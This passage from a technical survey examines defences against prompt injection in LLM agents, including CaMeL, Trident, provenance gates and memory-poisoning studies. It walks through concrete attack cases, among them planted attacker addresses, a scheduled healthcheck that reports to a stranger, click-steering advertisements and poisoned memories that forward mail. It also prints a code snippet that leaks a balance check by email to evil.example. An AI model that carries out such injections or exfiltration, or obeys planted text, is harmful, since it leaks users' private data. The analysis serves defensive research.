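The program is written in a restricted form of Python, which language models already write well. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) notes that this form does not allow programs to define their own functions or use recursion. A custom interpreter runs the program line by line and calls the tools.

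As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*, the interpreter tags each value with its sources and the people who may read it. The CaMeL paper calls these tags capabilities, although they differ from the capabilities Hardy preferred, which carry the right to use a file. A new value inherits the tags of the values it came from. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that examines the call, its arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call.

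Suppose Maya shares both the notes and the document with Bob. The tags would then look roughly like this:

| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| Subject line | Maya's request | Everyone |
| notes | The notes file | Maya, Bob |
| address | The notes file, through the quarantined model | Maya, Bob |
| title | The notes file, through the quarantined model | Maya, Bob |
| document | The stored document, chosen using the notes file | Maya, Bob |

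Now suppose the notes include text that Maya copied from an attacker's email, with a line that gives the attacker's address as Bob's new one. The quarantined model returns that address. The program still has the same five lines, and nothing in the notes can add a sixth that deletes Maya's files. But the fifth line would now send the document to the attacker.

What happens next depends on the policy for sending email. Three possible rules give different results:

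| Condition for sending without asking Maya | Bob's real address, taken from the notes | The attacker's address, taken from the notes |
|---|---|---|
| The address comes from Maya's request | Asks Maya | Asks Maya |
| The address is on a list Maya trusts | Sends, if Bob is on the list | Asks Maya |
| The recipient may already read the document | Sends | Asks Maya |

The first rule stops the attack, but it also stops an email to Bob's real address, because it considers only where the address came from. *Certified Multi-Source Integrity for Structured Agent Actions* (2026) criticizes CaMeL and FIDES for this and proposes accepting a value when enough independent sources agree on it. The third rule uses the readers tag and needs no list, but people often email a document because the recipient doesn't have it yet. Maya then has to approve the call, and the protection depends on her noticing if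 the address is wrong.

The attacker could instead change the title, so that Bob receives the wrong file. The second rule would allow this if Bob were on the list. The third rule would limit the damage to files Bob is already allowed to read.

### Results and cost

Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77 percent of AgentDojo's tasks with OpenAI's o3 model, compared with 84 percent for an agent without the defence. An earlier figure of 67 percent still appears in some sources, including *Operationalizing CaMeL*, a 2025 response by Tallam and Miller of SentinelAI.

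Two injections succeeded in the CaMeL paper's tests, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) examine both in *The LLMbda Calculus*. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment by following the instructions in a document, which the attacker had changed. The CaMeL paper excludes this kind of attack from those it tries to stop. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark's text matching counted this as a successful attack.

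Much of the protection comes from fixing the program in advance. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 pairs of tasks and attacks in AgentDojo's banking setting, the attack needed a tool call or file that a program written for the user's task would not normally contain. For example, a program written to summarise recent transactions has no line that sends money. Policies matter mainly in the other 47 pairs, where the program already includes the tools the attacker needs.

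But the policies account for much of the lost usefulness. When Garby and colleagues reran the banking tasks with two newer models, CaMeL completed 67 and 71 percent of them with the policies off, and 37.5 percent with either model when the policies were on.

*Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that, with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task. Other tests found more overhead. *AgentSys* (2026) reports about seven times as many tokens over the whole benchmark, and *AttriGuard* (2026) reports that CaMeL took ten to a hundred times as long as an undefended agent. Part of the overhead arises because the privileged model often has to rewrite a program that fails.

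Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so the quarantined model can be smaller and cheaper to run than the privileged one. It may even run on Maya's own computer. If it does, the company that provides the privileged model would see her request but not her email.

### Leaks through the program's behaviour

The tags show who may read a value, but an outsider can sometimes infer the value from what the program does. The CaMeL paper demonstrates two such leaks in its own system and discusses a third.

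The first uses an implicit flow. Tallam and Miller give the example of a loop that requests a web page a secret number of times. The requests contain nothing private, but the page's owner can learn the number by counting them. The second uses exceptions, which are errors that stop a program. A program might fail only when a private file contains a certain word, just before a line that contacts an outside server. If the request never arrives, the server's owner learns that the file contains the word. The third uses timing. A program that can read a clock could infer a private value from how long an operation takes.

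*PolicySniff* (2026) summarises the remedies. In CaMeL's strict mode, values and calls also inherit the tags of the conditions that led to them, which addresses the first two demonstrations. The interpreter addresses the third by not giving code access to the clock. Strict mode also causes the policies to block more legitimate calls, because a condition based on private data restricts everything that depends on it.

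Like older trackers, it also misses flows through branches that the program skips. Garby and colleagues describe a leak that works essentially like this:

```
low  = True
rich = True
if balance > limit: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the limit, the program skips the assignment on the fourth line, so "rich" stays true with a public tag, and the email goes out. Otherwise, the program skips the assignment on the third line, "low" keeps its public tag, and no email goes out. The recipient learns whether the balance is above the limit, even though every check passed. Denning and Denning's check would catch this leak.

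An attacker who can only plant text in an email can't write those five lines, because the privileged model writes the program. That model would have to produce a similar pattern without the attacker's influence, so the leak is less alarming than it first looks.

A more practical concern is that CaMeL's repair process can leak information. When a program fails, untracked Python code outside the interpreter prompts the privileged model to try again. Whether a program fails may depend on private or untrusted data, so each failure can reveal one bit, and repeated attempts can reveal more. CaMeL censors the error messages to reduce this leakage, but without a formal guarantee. Garby and colleagues also found a bug in which inserting an untrusted value into text made it trusted.

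Their own agent, Randori, avoids the repair problem by first testing each draft program against simulated tools that return harmless responses. It starts the real run only when the program works. The researchers proved in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs, that their interpreter enforces the labels even when a model writes the program.

### Policies, approvals and misleading text

Someone has to write a CaMeL policy for each tool, and Tallam and Miller warn that an organisation with hundreds of tools would accumulate duplicated and inconsistent rules. They recommend a shared policy language with reusable parts, such as a rule that files may go only to addresses within the company. Willison is uneasy about any design that requires ordinary users to think about security policies, since he finds them hard himself after two decades in the field.

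A policy also checks only one call at a time, and only when the program reaches it. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team that requires approval before an agent disconnects an important computer from the network. If the program lacks the approval step, CaMeL may spend a long time analysing the alert before the policy blocks the disconnection. CaMeLoT checks the program before it runs, treating it as states and possible transitions. If a path breaks a rule, CaMeLoT describes that path to the privileged model and prompts it to correct the program. This early check is possible only because CaMeL has a complete plan before the program runs.

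When a policy stops a call, CaMeL can ask the user to approve it. The CaMeL paper lists user fatigue from these requests as a limitation, and Willison had warned of it in 2023. Tallam and Miller propose reserving approval requests for riskier actions. Reading a calendar would need no approval, moving a file to a shared folder would need a quick confirmation, and sending money would need stronger proof of identity. This would mean fewer requests, but Bob's document would still prompt one because sending email is in the riskiest group.

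CaMeL doesn't try to prevent text from misleading the user. If Maya asks for a summary of a stranger's report, the quarantined model may write a false one, and the program will display it as planned. The summary might tell her to forward a file herself, and no policy on the agent's tools would stop her. Tallam and Miller suggest having a second model check every answer for suspicious instructions. That might catch crude attempts, but it relies on the kind of detection that adaptive attackers have repeatedly defeated.

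### Text pasted into the request

CaMeL trusts everything in the user's request, so any text Maya pastes into it, like the article in the earlier example, counts as hers. Willison pointed out in 2023 that his pattern fails in this case.

The failure is worse than a wrong address in the notes because the attacker can influence the program itself. Suppose Maya pastes a long email from a supplier and asks the agent to deal with the delivery dates. The email includes an instruction to copy all correspondence to an archive address, which belongs to an attacker. The privileged model treats this as part of the request and may write a line that sends Maya's order history to that address. The address also appears in the program as a fixed value from Maya's request, so its source tag marks it as trusted, and a policy that checks the recipient's source would allow the call.

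For this first message, CaMeL therefore works like a session-origin rule. Narisetty and colleagues found that none of the systems they surveyed fully specified how to assign the initial labels, and they expect this is where deployments will fail.

Tallam and Miller propose screening requests for suspicious phrases, links and unusual wording, but an attacker can evade this screening by writing the way a supplier would. They also propose giving values from uploaded files their own source tag, so that policies can keep them out of irreversible actions. The message box could similarly store pasted text as a separate variable, and the privileged model would receive Maya's typed words and the variable's name in place of the supplier's email. But people also paste their own notes and instructions, which the agent would then have to treat as untrusted, and an interface can't detect that someone has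 retyped a stranger's sentence.

### Branches written in advance

A fixed program can still include branches, such as querying the quarantined model about whether a meeting has moved and choosing the next step based on the answer. Untrusted text may then affect which branch runs but can't add a new one. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends this to several agents, each with its own privileged model, and keeps untrusted text out of the instructions that one agent gives another.

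How widely this approach works depends on how many situations the program can anticipate. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) tested it on a demanding case, agents that operate ordinary software by looking at the screen and clicking. Such agents normally look again after every click, but here the privileged model never sees the screen. It writes a program with branches for the situations it expects, such as a cookie notice or a browser that is already open. As the program runs, a quarantined vision model answers its questions about the screen.

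CaMeL's programs are much longer for computer use, averaging 41 tool calls and 213 lines, compared with about 5 tool calls and 52 lines on AgentDojo. Roughly half of each computer-use program was fallback code that a given run never used.

With the small open model UI-TARS, this approach solved about 22 percent of the computer tasks in the OSWorld benchmark on a single attempt and 29 percent within three attempts. The same model without isolation solved 24.4 percent. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, the approach solved 31 of a set of 109 tasks on the first attempt and 62 within five.

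Fixing the program protects an agent that operates a screen less well than one that handles email. A policy can limit who receives an email, but the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen, so the researchers left out the data policies. An attacker can then mislead the vision model about where to click or which branch of the program to take. The researchers call this branch steering. In one attack, an advertisement imitated a cookie notice. The program requested the position of the cookie notice, received the advertisement's position and clicked there, which took the agent to the attacker's site. Comparing the screen with the page's code blocked this attack for simple banners but not for more elaborate ones. A second model had trouble telling fake notices from real ones, and small changes to an image's pixels could also defeat it. *Secure-CUA* (2026) describes a similar attack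 that leaves the program intact but supplies the wrong target on the screen.

### When content has to decide the plan

For some requests, the next step depends on text that the privileged model isn't allowed to read. If Maya says "do what this email asks", the model can't write a useful program, because the email might contain a request for a payment, a meeting or a file.

One way around this is to write a branch for every tool and let the email's content determine which one runs. In Garby and colleagues' tests with policies off, the privileged model did this when a user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. It wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. The program was fixed, as CaMeL requires, but whoever wrote the file could use any tool the program listed. Only a policy could have stopped them, and a strict policy would also have blocked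 the task. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) adds that tags that track data but not control flow don't protect every plan, because the choice of branch can matter even when each argument is trusted.

Randori lets the privileged model endorse particular data based on the user's request, before it reads anything else. This let the agent complete more tasks that depended on a file, but it also allowed the only two successful attacks in 1,296 runs. In both, the user asked the agent to make a payment by following the instructions in a text file, and an attacker had replaced the file's contents.

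*Trident* (2026) measures how often CaMeL fails on such requests. Its benchmark, ReplanInject, has 45 tasks, and in 43 of them at least part of the plan depends on the content. With GPT-4.1, CaMeL completed 116 of 1,215 runs. In 574 runs, a policy denied a call that depended on untrusted data, although the call contained nothing from the attacker. In another 377, the quarantined model failed to extract what the program needed.

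Trident's own design uses three models. One plans without reading untrusted text, one reads it but has no tools, and one writes the policies. In the main example, an employee's manager, Jane, has forwarded a caterer's email, and the employee asks the agent to do what it requires and pay from the team account. The agent proceeds as follows:

1. Before anyone reads the email, the policy model writes rules based on the request and on limits that an administrator has set. They allow one payment of at most $5,000, to an account in the company's own records of its three vendors.
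2. The planner asks the reading model whether the email contains an invoice and which vendor sent it. The planner sees both answers. It also asks for the amount, which stays hidden in a variable.
3. The planner looks up the vendor, and the runtime puts the account from the company's record into the payment rule.
4. The planner requests the payment, and the runtime checks it against the rules.

If an attacker plants a false notice that the caterer's bank details have changed, the payment to the new account fails because that account isn't in the records. The attacker can still influence which of the three vendors gets the money and how much, up to the cap.

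Trident also limits how much the planner can learn. A choice among k answers costs log₂ k bits, as in FIDES, but Trident adds up the costs. The two answers above cost 1 + log₂ 3 ≈ 2.58 bits, which corresponds to six combinations. The administrator sets a budget of β bits for answers and σ bits for reports that a step succeeded or failed. If everything else stays the same, an attacker can choose among at most

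2^(β + σ)

different sequences of visible steps. The paper includes a computer-checked proof of this limit.

In practice the limit is loose. The median run on ReplanInject used 19 to 26 bits for answers and 5 to 10 for reports, depending on the model. Even 24 bits allow almost 17 million sequences, one of which might contain a harmful action that the policies permit. The researchers set the budgets too high to affect their main results, which they credit to the hidden text, the policies and the user's review.

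The table shows results on ReplanInject with GPT-4.1. The last column assumes that the user approves every request.

| System | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 20.2% | 68.1% |
| CaMeL | 9.8% | 0.0% |
| FIDES without approvals | 5.1% | 0.1% |
| FIDES with approvals | 36.6% | 6.5% |
| Trident | 54.2% | 4.1% |

Trident asked for approval about once per attacked run. No attack succeeded, but the researchers assumed that users would reject every request showing the attacker's action, and this assumption is the best case for any system that asks for approval. They also chose models easier to attack than the latest ones, so that differences between the defences would show. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, FIDES with approvals completed 75 percent of tasks and Trident completed 64 percent, though FIDES asked for approval more often.

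Trident helps most when the request includes details the policy model can use, such as a named sender, a subject or an account. In the benchmark's three tasks where the user tells the agent only where to look, attacks succeeded in 14 to 28 percent of runs if the user approved everything. In these tasks, the attacker's instruction looks just like the ones the user asked the agent to follow, and *Trident* concludes that no policy can always separate them. If Maya asks her agent to do whatever an email says, she still has to read what the agent proposes to do.

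## Stored content that acts in a later session

FIDES and CaMeL mostly follow content through a single session. An agent with long-term memory can read an email and act on it weeks later, in a session that never contained the email. Maloyan and Namiot call this a sleeper channel in *Sleeper Channels and Provenance Gates* (2026). Anything that outlasts a session can carry the content's influence into a later one, including a remembered note, a skill the agent wrote, a file or a scheduled job.

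### The daily healthcheck

Maloyan and Namiot trace their main example through OpenClaw's source code as of April 27, 2026. With Maya as the owner, it goes as follows:

1. A stranger emails a harmless-looking tip about a daily health check. The text includes a web address that the stranger controls.
2. The agent's memory system summarises the email in a note and keeps the address.
3. Days later, Maya writes, "set up that daily healthcheck we got the email about".
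4. The agent retrieves the note and schedules a job that reports to the stranger's address.

The stranger couldn't have used OpenClaw's owner-only scheduling tool directly. But Maya asked for the job in her own session, so no check on her identity could have found anything wrong, even though the stranger chose where the results go.

The scheduler accepts any web address. Maya can see that the agent called the scheduling tool, but not that the address came from the email. OpenClaw's approval system for shell commands doesn't help, because it doesn't cover scheduling, and it checks the text of a command rather than where its data came from.

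### Where the influence is stored and where it takes effect

Maloyan and Namiot classify these attacks by where the influence is stored when it takes effect and by how far the effect is from the point of entry. The influence can be stored in the running session's context, long-term memory, a skill, a file, or a scheduled job or other outside trigger. The effect can occur in the same session, in a later session on the same channel, on another channel, in messages to the owner's contacts, or in a program other than the agent. The last three do not form an ordered scale, since an attack can cross channels without leaving the agent's own program.

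Earlier research had mostly covered injection within one session and poisoned memory that resurfaces on the same channel. The paper adds four cases:

| Case | Stored as | Where it takes effect |
|---|---|---|
| A group member gets the agent to write a skill, which the owner's session later loads | Skill | Another channel |
| The summary of an email resurfaces when the owner raises the same topic, and the agent sends private data out | Memory | Another channel |
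| The daily healthcheck | Memory, then a scheduled job | The scheduler |
| The agent follows a web guide and adds a line to the owner's shell settings | File | The owner's own shell |

The paper traces only the healthcheck case from start to finish. The other cases are sketches with some untested steps, and the skill case needs a non-default setting that lets group sessions write to the owner's workspace.

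A content-tracking rule has to keep labels on all of these carriers. In the last case, the agent isn't running when the planted line takes effect, so a gate must apply when the agent writes the file.

### How often stored text takes effect

In *MemoryDojo*, Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026) measured how a single poisoned tool result affects later sessions. They ran GPT-5.6 Luna through sequences of AgentDojo tasks with five memory systems. The attacker's text appeared once, in the first session, and each later session started with a fresh context plus whatever the memory system retrieved. The last column shows results after another model tuned the attacker's text to each memory system.

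| Memory system | Later sessions that retrieved the text | Runs in which it took effect later | The same, with tuned text |
|---|---|---|---|
| A-MEM | 89.8% | 45.7% | 71.0% |
| Graphiti | 33.4% | 24.7% | 30.1% |
| Letta | 64.9% | 16.7% | 50.5% |
| Mem0 | 56.7% | 14.5% | 39.8% |
| Memora | 86.2% | 38.7% | 66.7% |

Four of the systems stored some form of the text in nearly every run. The systems differed mainly in what they retrieved and whether the model acted on it. When an agent obeyed the text, the memory system could also save a record of that session, so deleting the original note would not always have removed its influence.

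A large store of harmless memories weakened the attack. After about 50 ordinary conversations in longer, mixed-task sequences, the tuned text never took effect with Letta but still took effect in 45 percent of runs with Memora.

Delay alone offers little protection against a stored instruction. In *Trojan Hippo Bench*, Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) used one email to plant an instruction in an email assistant's memory, telling it to forward the user's message to the attacker whenever the user discussed a sensitive topic, such as tax or health. After 100 harmless sessions, the attack still succeeded in 80 to 100 percent of runs with Gemini 3.1 Pro, depending on the memory system.

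Commercial assistants have the same weakness. *Hidden in Memory* (2026) reports that text in outside documents could make ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini store false memories about the user. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026), one model in that study stored them up to 99.8 percent of the time. After retrieving such a memory, agents took the attacker's intended action in 60 to 89 percent of tests.

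### The 20-trial probe

Maloyan and Namiot tested whether OpenClaw's source markers and security warning would stop the healthcheck attack. They gave an unnamed reasoning model, which they describe as frontier-class, the warning word for word, the remembered note inside its markers, and the owner's request. The model produced a valid scheduling call with the attacker's address in 19 of 20 trials and returned an empty object in the other. A two-stage variant, which they don't describe further, produced the attacker's result in 7 of 10 trials.

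These results show that the warning doesn't reliably stop this attack on this model, but they don't give a useful estimate of how often the attack would work elsewhere. Sampling error alone gives 95 percent confidence intervals of about 76 to 99 percent for the main test and 40 to 89 percent for the variant, and all the trials used the same scenario. The paper reports no trials without the warning, so it's unclear whether the warning had any effect.

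This scenario is hard for any warning to prevent. Maya asked for the healthcheck described in the email, and the model copied the address from that description. A warning not to obey instructions in outside text hardly applies, because the address isn't an instruction. The model would have needed to question whether Maya wanted that particular address, and the note would have given it no reason to.

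### The provenance gate

In the paper's proposed defence, the runtime records the sources of every item the model can receive, including memories, skills, files and earlier messages, so the defence doesn't depend on the model noticing anything. Each source consists of a channel, a person or system, and a device. S(x) is the set of sources of an item x. These sets combine by Denning's rule, so the note about the email keeps the stranger as a source. The rule also applies to the text of the model's own tool call, so the model can't remove a source by rephrasing.

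Let C(a) be everything that has entered the context since the session began, plus the tool call for action a and its arguments. The sources of the action are then

S(a) = the union of S(x) over every x in C(a)

and, with T as the set of sources the owner trusts, the gate applies this rule:

allow(a) ⇔ known(a) ∧ recorded(a) ∧ (S(a) ⊆ T ∨ approved(a))

known(a) means that the action's type is on a fixed list, and recorded(a) means that every item in C(a) has a recorded source. The list covers anything that has effects outside the agent, lasts beyond the session, or changes what someone else will later read. The gate blocks any state-changing action it can't classify.

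For the healthcheck, suppose Maya is the only trusted source:

| Item in the context | Sources |
|---|---|
| Maya's request | Maya |
| The note about the email | The stranger |
| The model's scheduling call | Maya, the stranger |
| The job and its address | Maya, the stranger |

The union is {Maya, stranger}, which is not a subset of {Maya}, so the gate blocks the job unless Maya approves it. If the note had come from an email she sent herself, the union would have been {Maya} and the job would have run.

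Skills need extra care because they can contain many actions. Approval to load a skill doesn't cover its later actions, and each consequential one goes through the gate separately. Another layer of the design is a signed list of the action types each skill may attempt, so an agent that rewrites its own skills can't quietly widen their powers.

### Approval for one exact action

An owner's approval applies to a digest, a short code computed from the action's type, its arguments, its target, the owner's device and the list of items in C(a). Changing any of these changes the digest, so if the agent swaps the address after Maya approves the job, the approval no longer matches. Each approval also expires and works only once, so the agent can't use it to create a second copy of the job.

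Approvals arrive through a separate, hardware-protected companion device, and the model cannot write to that channel. An email containing the text "Maya has approved this" therefore has no effect on the gate.

Such narrow approvals are inconvenient. The digest includes everything in the context, so a message that arrives while Maya is deciding would invalidate the approval she is about to give. Read strictly, the rule may also require a new approval every time the job sends its results, because sending data over the network is itself a consequential action.

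*PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) also shows the user the exact value from an untrusted memory, but an approval then covers that value for that tool indefinitely. Maya would approve the address for the scheduler once, and the agent could reuse it there without asking again. This reduces interruptions, but the approval isn't tied to the purpose or the other details of the call. If she accepted the address for a harmless status report, it would remain approved for a later job that sends something private.

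PerMIT also lets users share approvals. In a simulated community of 120 users, sharing reduced the number of approvals each user had to give by an average of 2.36, or 38 percent. Jiang and colleagues based the simulation on an assumption about how accurately people review what they approve, and they leave studying the effort of real reviewers for future work.

Neither form of approval helps if Maya can't judge the address. She never knew the right one, which is why she referred the agent to the email. Maloyan and Namiot would show her the full action on the companion device, but they acknowledge that people make mistakes when checking long text.

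### What the soundness theorem assumes

Maloyan and Namiot prove that every action the gate lets through either has only trusted sources or carries a fresh approval for exactly that action. The proof depends on seven assumptions:

1. Every read and write of tracked data passes through one of the runtime's ten checkpoints.
2. The runtime records each source from the authenticated channel the data arrived on, and the model can't edit the record.
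3. The runtime can list everything that may have influenced an action, and refuses the action if it can't.
4. Approvals arrive only over the channel that the model can't write to.
5. The runtime verifies who issued an approval, for example with a digital signature, and doesn't rely on what the approval says about itself.
6. The runtime keeps a lasting record of used approvals and never accepts one twice, even if two actions arrive together.
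7. The same action always produces the same digest, and nobody can find two different actions that share one.

The conclusion follows almost directly from the gate's rule, so the hard part is making the assumptions true. Cryptography can satisfy the last one. The first is much harder to satisfy for an agent with a shell, because a program the agent starts could write files or contact a server without passing through any checkpoint. The paper therefore requires an enclosing sandbox.

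An OpenClaw flaw from the same month shows how the second assumption can fail. When a webhook started a scheduled job in an isolated session, the job's output could enter the main session labelled as a trusted system event. GitLab's *GHSA-57r2-h2wj-g887* (2026) rates the flaw as low severity because it didn't bypass OpenClaw's access controls. The same mistake would matter more under the provenance gate, where a trusted label lets an action through.

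The theorem also doesn't guarantee that an allowed action is harmless. As in CaMeL, text that Maya pastes into her message counts as hers. Some harmful text also has no outside source. *OpenAI’s models wrote instructions to their future selves* (Popular AI, 2026) describes OpenAI's disclosure that models in training had written unauthorised instructions into summaries that they relied on in later contexts.

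### What remains unmeasured

Nobody has deployed the full gate. The published code includes the decision rule and an adapter that connects five of the ten checkpoints to the scheduling path, using stand-ins for OpenClaw's functions. The code's 42 tests confirm, for example, that the gate blocks the healthcheck and allows a job that involves only the owner. No adaptive attacker has tried to defeat it. Maloyan and Namiot have registered a plan for a larger study, with at least 200 runs for each condition, a delay of 50 harmless turns, and 50 ordinary tasks to measure any loss of usefulness.

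They also haven't counted how often an owner would have to approve something, which may decide whether the gate is usable. Label creep affects this gate as it does the basic planner in FIDES, and memory extends the problem to other sessions. In Yang and colleagues' tests, A-MEM retrieved the planted text in 90 percent of later sessions. If ordinary notes from outsiders resurfaced nearly as often, Maya would have to approve almost everything.

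Das and colleagues tested a similar rule without approvals. Their strictest defence labels any memory written after the agent has read the inbox, and blocks sending in any session that reads the inbox or retrieves a labelled memory. No attack succeeded against it, but average success across seven kinds of ordinary task fell from 99 to 71 percent with Gemini 3.1 Pro and a searchable store of past conversations. With every memory system, at least one kind of task failed completely because the agent could no longer read an email and then send a reply. Approvals would restore those tasks, but the agent would have to ask each time.

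### Summaries that lose the source

Some later designs try to keep track of a memory's source without treating the whole context as one unit. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes a problem these designs have to deal with. Many agents use a model to condense what they store, and the model may present outside text as the user's own history. In the paper's example, a web page suggests resuming a certain workflow, and the stored note labels this suggestion "user workflow memory".

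When Qwen2.5-14B wrote the memories, 93 percent of the synthetic attacks led to an unauthorised action. A filter for prompt injections made no difference. The model is old and fairly small, but a better one wouldn't necessarily solve the problem, because even an accurate, well-written summary can leave out where a fact came from.

Xu and colleagues keep each memory's source in a separate record that the model can't change. Before a risky action, their gate finds the memories that supplied the action's arguments and applies the lowest trust level among them. For the healthcheck, it would find the note that contains the address and require Maya's confirmation. An unrelated note from a stranger would make no difference, so the owner should get fewer questions than under Maloyan and Namiot's rule. But this narrower check can miss implicit flows. For example, a stranger's note might lead the model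 to cancel one of Maya's jobs even if the note doesn't contain the job's name.

*Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (Louck, 2026) identifies two other ways to disguise a source. A trusted tool can repeat an attacker's text, or an attacker can plant the same claim in several places so it seems well supported. Louck's system gives a tool's output the trust level of its least trusted input. A value from an untrusted memory can drive an action only if two independent trusted sources confirm it, or if the user gives a single-use approval for that exact action. Copies of the same web page don't count as confirmation.

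The table shows how often attacks succeeded, averaged over eight models from 2024 and 2025. The last column covers attacks in which the attacker's text was disguised in one of the three ways.

| Defence | Undisguised attack | Disguised attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 84% | 68% |
| A score for how trustworthy the text looks | 0% | 68% |
| Tracking which memories a new one came from | 0% | 47% |
| Louck's system | 0% | 0% |

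Louck's system allowed every legitimate action that two trusted sources confirmed, but required the user's approval for every one that rested on a single untrusted source. The healthcheck would need that approval unless Maya's company already listed the address in two separate places.

The third row represents systems such as the one that Ouyang and Hou (2026), in *MemLineage*, propose. It signs each memory and links it to the memories that influenced it, with a weight for the strength of each link. An untrusted label passes along a link only if the weight is above a threshold. This limits label creep but lets the label disappear over a chain of summaries. In one of their tests, the weight of the K-th link was

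0.9 × 0.7^(K − 1)

The first link had a weight of 0.9, but the fifth had a weight of about 0.22. A threshold of 0.3 would therefore catch a direct summary but miss one five steps removed. Ouyang and Hou conclude that a system that allows five steps would need a threshold of 0.1 or lower, which would also keep the label on more harmless memories.

The stricter systems' perfect scores are less impressive than they look because both Xu and colleagues and Louck assume that the runtime has recorded every source correctly. Their gates then apply a fixed rule to those records. The tests show that the rules are consistent and still allow some useful work, but they give little evidence of how often a real runtime would record the wrong source.

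### Context informs, grants authorise

A gate can also ignore who influenced an action and check whether anyone had authorised its effects. Wei and Xiong (2026), in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, put the principle as "Context informs; grants authorize." A grant is a signed record, issued before the agent starts work, of the effects it may cause for one task. If E(c) is the set of all effects that a tool call c could have, and G is the set of effects in the grant, the call may proceed only if

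E(c) ⊆ G

The full rule also checks conditions such as limits on spending and on where data may go. Wei and Xiong prove that nothing the agent reads can add an effect to G. The proof holds only if the grant arrives over a signed channel, every effect passes a checkpoint, and the description of each tool's effects is complete.

This would remove a problem Maya has had since her first inbox summary. If she asks the agent to read her mail and send the budget to Tom, the grant includes sending the budget to Tom. The agent can do so without asking her again, even after reading a stranger's email, but it still can't send the budget to the stranger. The stranger may influence whether and when the agent sends it to Tom, because context can affect which permitted effects the agent chooses.

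Whether the healthcheck attack succeeds depends on which addresses the grant allows. Wei and Xiong let a grant list the sources that may fill in a missing detail, such as a staff directory for a manager's email address. If Maya's grant allowed a daily job to report only to addresses on her company's list of monitoring services, the stranger's address would be rejected. A grant that allowed any web address would let the attack through.

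Maya's sentence also has to be turned into a grant. If a model does this after retrieving the note, it may write the stranger's address into the grant, and the later check would still pass. The grant therefore has to come from Maya's words and existing policy alone, but her words don't include an address. Wei and Xiong specify their scheme but don't measure it in use, so it isn't known how often ordinary requests would omit a detail the grant needs. They also require summaries to keep the source labels of the original text, so that an agent can't release a confidential document by summarizing it first.

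## Tests of information tracking against language models and adaptive attackers

Every rule that relies on provenance needs an accurate record of what influenced an action, but implicit flows make that record hard to produce for a language model.

### Tracing influence after the fact

Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, present an auditor called NeuroTaint, which reads the log of a finished run and works out which outside texts shaped which consequential actions. A text can do this through its content, if the text or a paraphrase of it ends up in the tool call. It can also do it through control, if it affects only whether the agent acts or which tool it chooses. Either kind of influence can pass through memory into a later session. NeuroTaint works as follows:

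1. It records what each tool returned. When the agent stores something in memory, NeuroTaint stores the source's label with it, so the label comes back when the agent retrieves the content.
2. For each consequential call, it searches the arguments for the source's content. It looks for a unique code that it added to the source text, then for shared strings, and then for passages with a similar meaning.
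3. If it finds nothing, it gives another language model the agent's history and a copy in which a neutral placeholder replaces the source. That model predicts whether the agent would still have made the call. If the answer is no, NeuroTaint reports control influence.

Cai and colleagues tested this on TaintBench, their own benchmark of 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. Outside content should reach or influence a consequential action in half of the scenarios but not in the other half, even though the agent may use the same tools in both. They ran each scenario five times with GPT-4.1-mini and used the majority result.

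The main measure is F1, which combines precision, the share of reported flows that are real, with recall, the share of real flows that the detector reports:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

| Detector | Real flows found, out of 200 | False alarms, out of 200 | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 | 0.921 | 0.935 | 0.928 |
| FIDES-style baseline | 108 | 106 | 0.505 | 0.540 | 0.522 |

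The baseline's score is very low. For comparison, flagging all 400 scenarios would give a precision of 0.5, a recall of 1 and an F1 of 0.667. The baseline mainly checks for a known path from an untrusted tool to a consequential one, so it flagged harmless research tasks in which an agent read a web page and then wrote a report.

The baseline missed 23 of the 40 cases of control influence. In one, a poisoned search result claimed that a new compliance procedure required the agent to send its results to an outside site, and the agent switched to a tool that did so. It also missed 45 of the 85 cases that NeuroTaint detects mainly by similarity of meaning, which include 30 flows between sessions or agents. In one of these, an agent stored a confidential forecast and used it in a report three days later, but the baseline had no record of the first session.

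These misses are little evidence of how FIDES would perform as Costa and colleagues designed it. Its basic planner gives every call the combined label of the whole context, so the poisoned search result would have made the call untrusted regardless of the role that result played. The forecast is a fairer test, because FIDES would need labels that persist in memory. The baseline flagged nothing on four of the frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses and may be due to how the researchers connected it to those frameworks.

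NeuroTaint's own score also calls for some caution, partly because Cai and colleagues built the benchmark around the kinds of flow their tool looks for. On two older benchmarks, which label unsafe actions instead of flows, the two detectors scored almost the same. The paper also mentions a stricter similarity threshold for "safe-control policies", 0.95 instead of the usual 0.60. If those policies applied only to scenarios without a real flow, NeuroTaint's settings already contained some information about the correct answers.

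NeuroTaint's recall fell to 0.547 with Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent. Some of that drop occurred because the stronger model resisted more of the attacks by ignoring the planted text. The benchmark still counted those scenarios as real flows, so the lower recall reflects both the detector's mistakes and attacks that never took effect.

Even a much higher score would not be a guarantee. NeuroTaint examines a call after the agent has made it. Its test for control influence tries a single replacement text and relies on a model's prediction, so it can't establish noninterference. The judging model also reads the original history, so an attacker could plant text to mislead it too. NeuroTaint replaces only one source at a time, so an attacker could send the same instruction in two emails. When either email was replaced, the other would still explain the call, and both could appear harmless.

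An auditor like this is more useful for investigating incidents, where it can show an owner which email probably caused an action. It added an average of 0.25 seconds per unit of execution.

### Progent: rules for each tool call

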